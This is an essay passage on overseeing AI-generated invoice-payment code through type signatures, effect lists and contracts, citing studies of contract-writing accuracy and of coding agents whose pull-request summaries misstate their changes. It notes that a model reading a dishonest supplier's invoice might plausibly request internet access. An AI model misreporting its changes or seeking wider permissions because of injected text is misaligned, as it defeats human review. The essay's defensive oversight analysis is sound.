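Here `pay` and `hold` are pure functions that only create a decision. The company's own loop calls `decide` once for each invoice and carries out the decision it gets back. Because ρ could be any type, `decide` can only return a value of that type by calling `pay` with an amount or `hold` with a reason.

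The loop carries out only the decision that the generated code returns, so the code can't silently skip an invoice or pay one twice. This achieves much of what the postcondition about `Paid` and `Held` required, without a solver or an invariant. The code can still choose a wrong amount or hold everything, so the company also needs a limit on the amount. The reasoning fails if the language lets code produce a ρ with `null` or an unchecked cast. The code may also throw an exception or run forever.

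### What a reviewer can learn from a signature

A person who approves a contract without reading the code has to judge what the contract leaves out. This is fairly easy for effects. The list `{Invoices, Pay, Report}` is complete and doesn't include `Net`, so the program can't contact other websites through the typed interface. The accountant can go through the labels and ask whether the program should have each power.

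Generated code can satisfy a contract and still be wrong if the contract omits a necessary postcondition. The contract for the shortest list looks reasonable, but it never requires the result to come from the collection. Even people who publish contracts as model answers overlook such gaps. Wang and colleagues selected 61 suspicious reference contracts from their 762 tasks and found probable defects in 36. When they restored a missing guarantee in one reference contract, 10 of the 11 generated contracts that had failed comparison with the original were equivalent to the corrected version. A reviewer who trusted the original would have wrongly faulted those 10.

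A concrete example may help a reviewer more than the formula does. A tool could search for an outcome that the contract permits but the company wouldn't expect, such as the answer [9], and show it to the reviewer, who decides whether it is acceptable. An accountant who can't read a postcondition can still see that a payment to an unknown supplier is wrong.

If the model also writes the signature, the effect list is still useful because the checker rejects a program that has an effect not on the list. The list may include effects the program doesn't need, but anyone who reads it can see them. However, a postcondition written by the same model may be true and still omit the guarantee that matters.

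*Verus-SpecGym* (Agarwal, Neamtu et al., 2026) tested whether models can write complete contracts from English descriptions. It used 581 problems from programming competitions and tested each contract on valid and invalid inputs and on right and wrong outputs. Some of the tests came from competitors who had tried to break each other's programs. Gemini 3.1 Pro wrote a contract that passed every test for 77.8% of the problems, while other leading models did so for 51.1% to 57.8%. Models often failed to write correct contracts for problems they could already solve in code. Newer models would probably do better, but contracts that are wrong about one time in five are a poor basis for approving payment code without reading it.

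Asking a second model to review the contract helps only partly. In the same study, a model acting as judge missed 26% of the faulty contracts that the tests caught. A reviewer can't rely on the coding agent's summary of its changes either, and needs to see the signature itself. *Analyzing Message-Code Inconsistency in AI Coding Agent-Authored Pull Requests* (2026) classified cases in which the summary didn't match the code. In 45.4% of them, the summary described changes that the agent hadn't made, and in 22.0% it left out significant ones. These are shares of the mismatches, not of all summaries, so they don't measure how often agents mislead reviewers.

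The hardest decision is whether to grant a model's request for more than the current contract allows. *Do AI Coding Agents Write Infrastructure as Code Like Humans?* found that 24.1% of the changes in which agents extended existing infrastructure broadened permissions, and recommends targeted review for such changes. Some were surely necessary, since a new feature often needs new access. But a model that has read a dishonest supplier's invoice may give an equally plausible reason for requesting the `Net` effect.

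The reviewer should therefore get the difference between the old and new effect lists from the compiler, not from the model. A short message such as "Adds `Net`" prompts the reviewer to ask why code that pays invoices now needs internet access. If the code needs it to look up an exchange rate, the company can fetch the rate itself.

Such requests also need to be rare. An accountant who has to approve a new permission every day would probably stop reading the requests, much as the paid testers in Anthropic's report caught fewer dangerous commands late in a session. A task that stays the same each month should almost never need a wider contract, so a request is a sign that something has changed. Refusing it does little harm, because the model can usually try again within the old limits before any money has moved.
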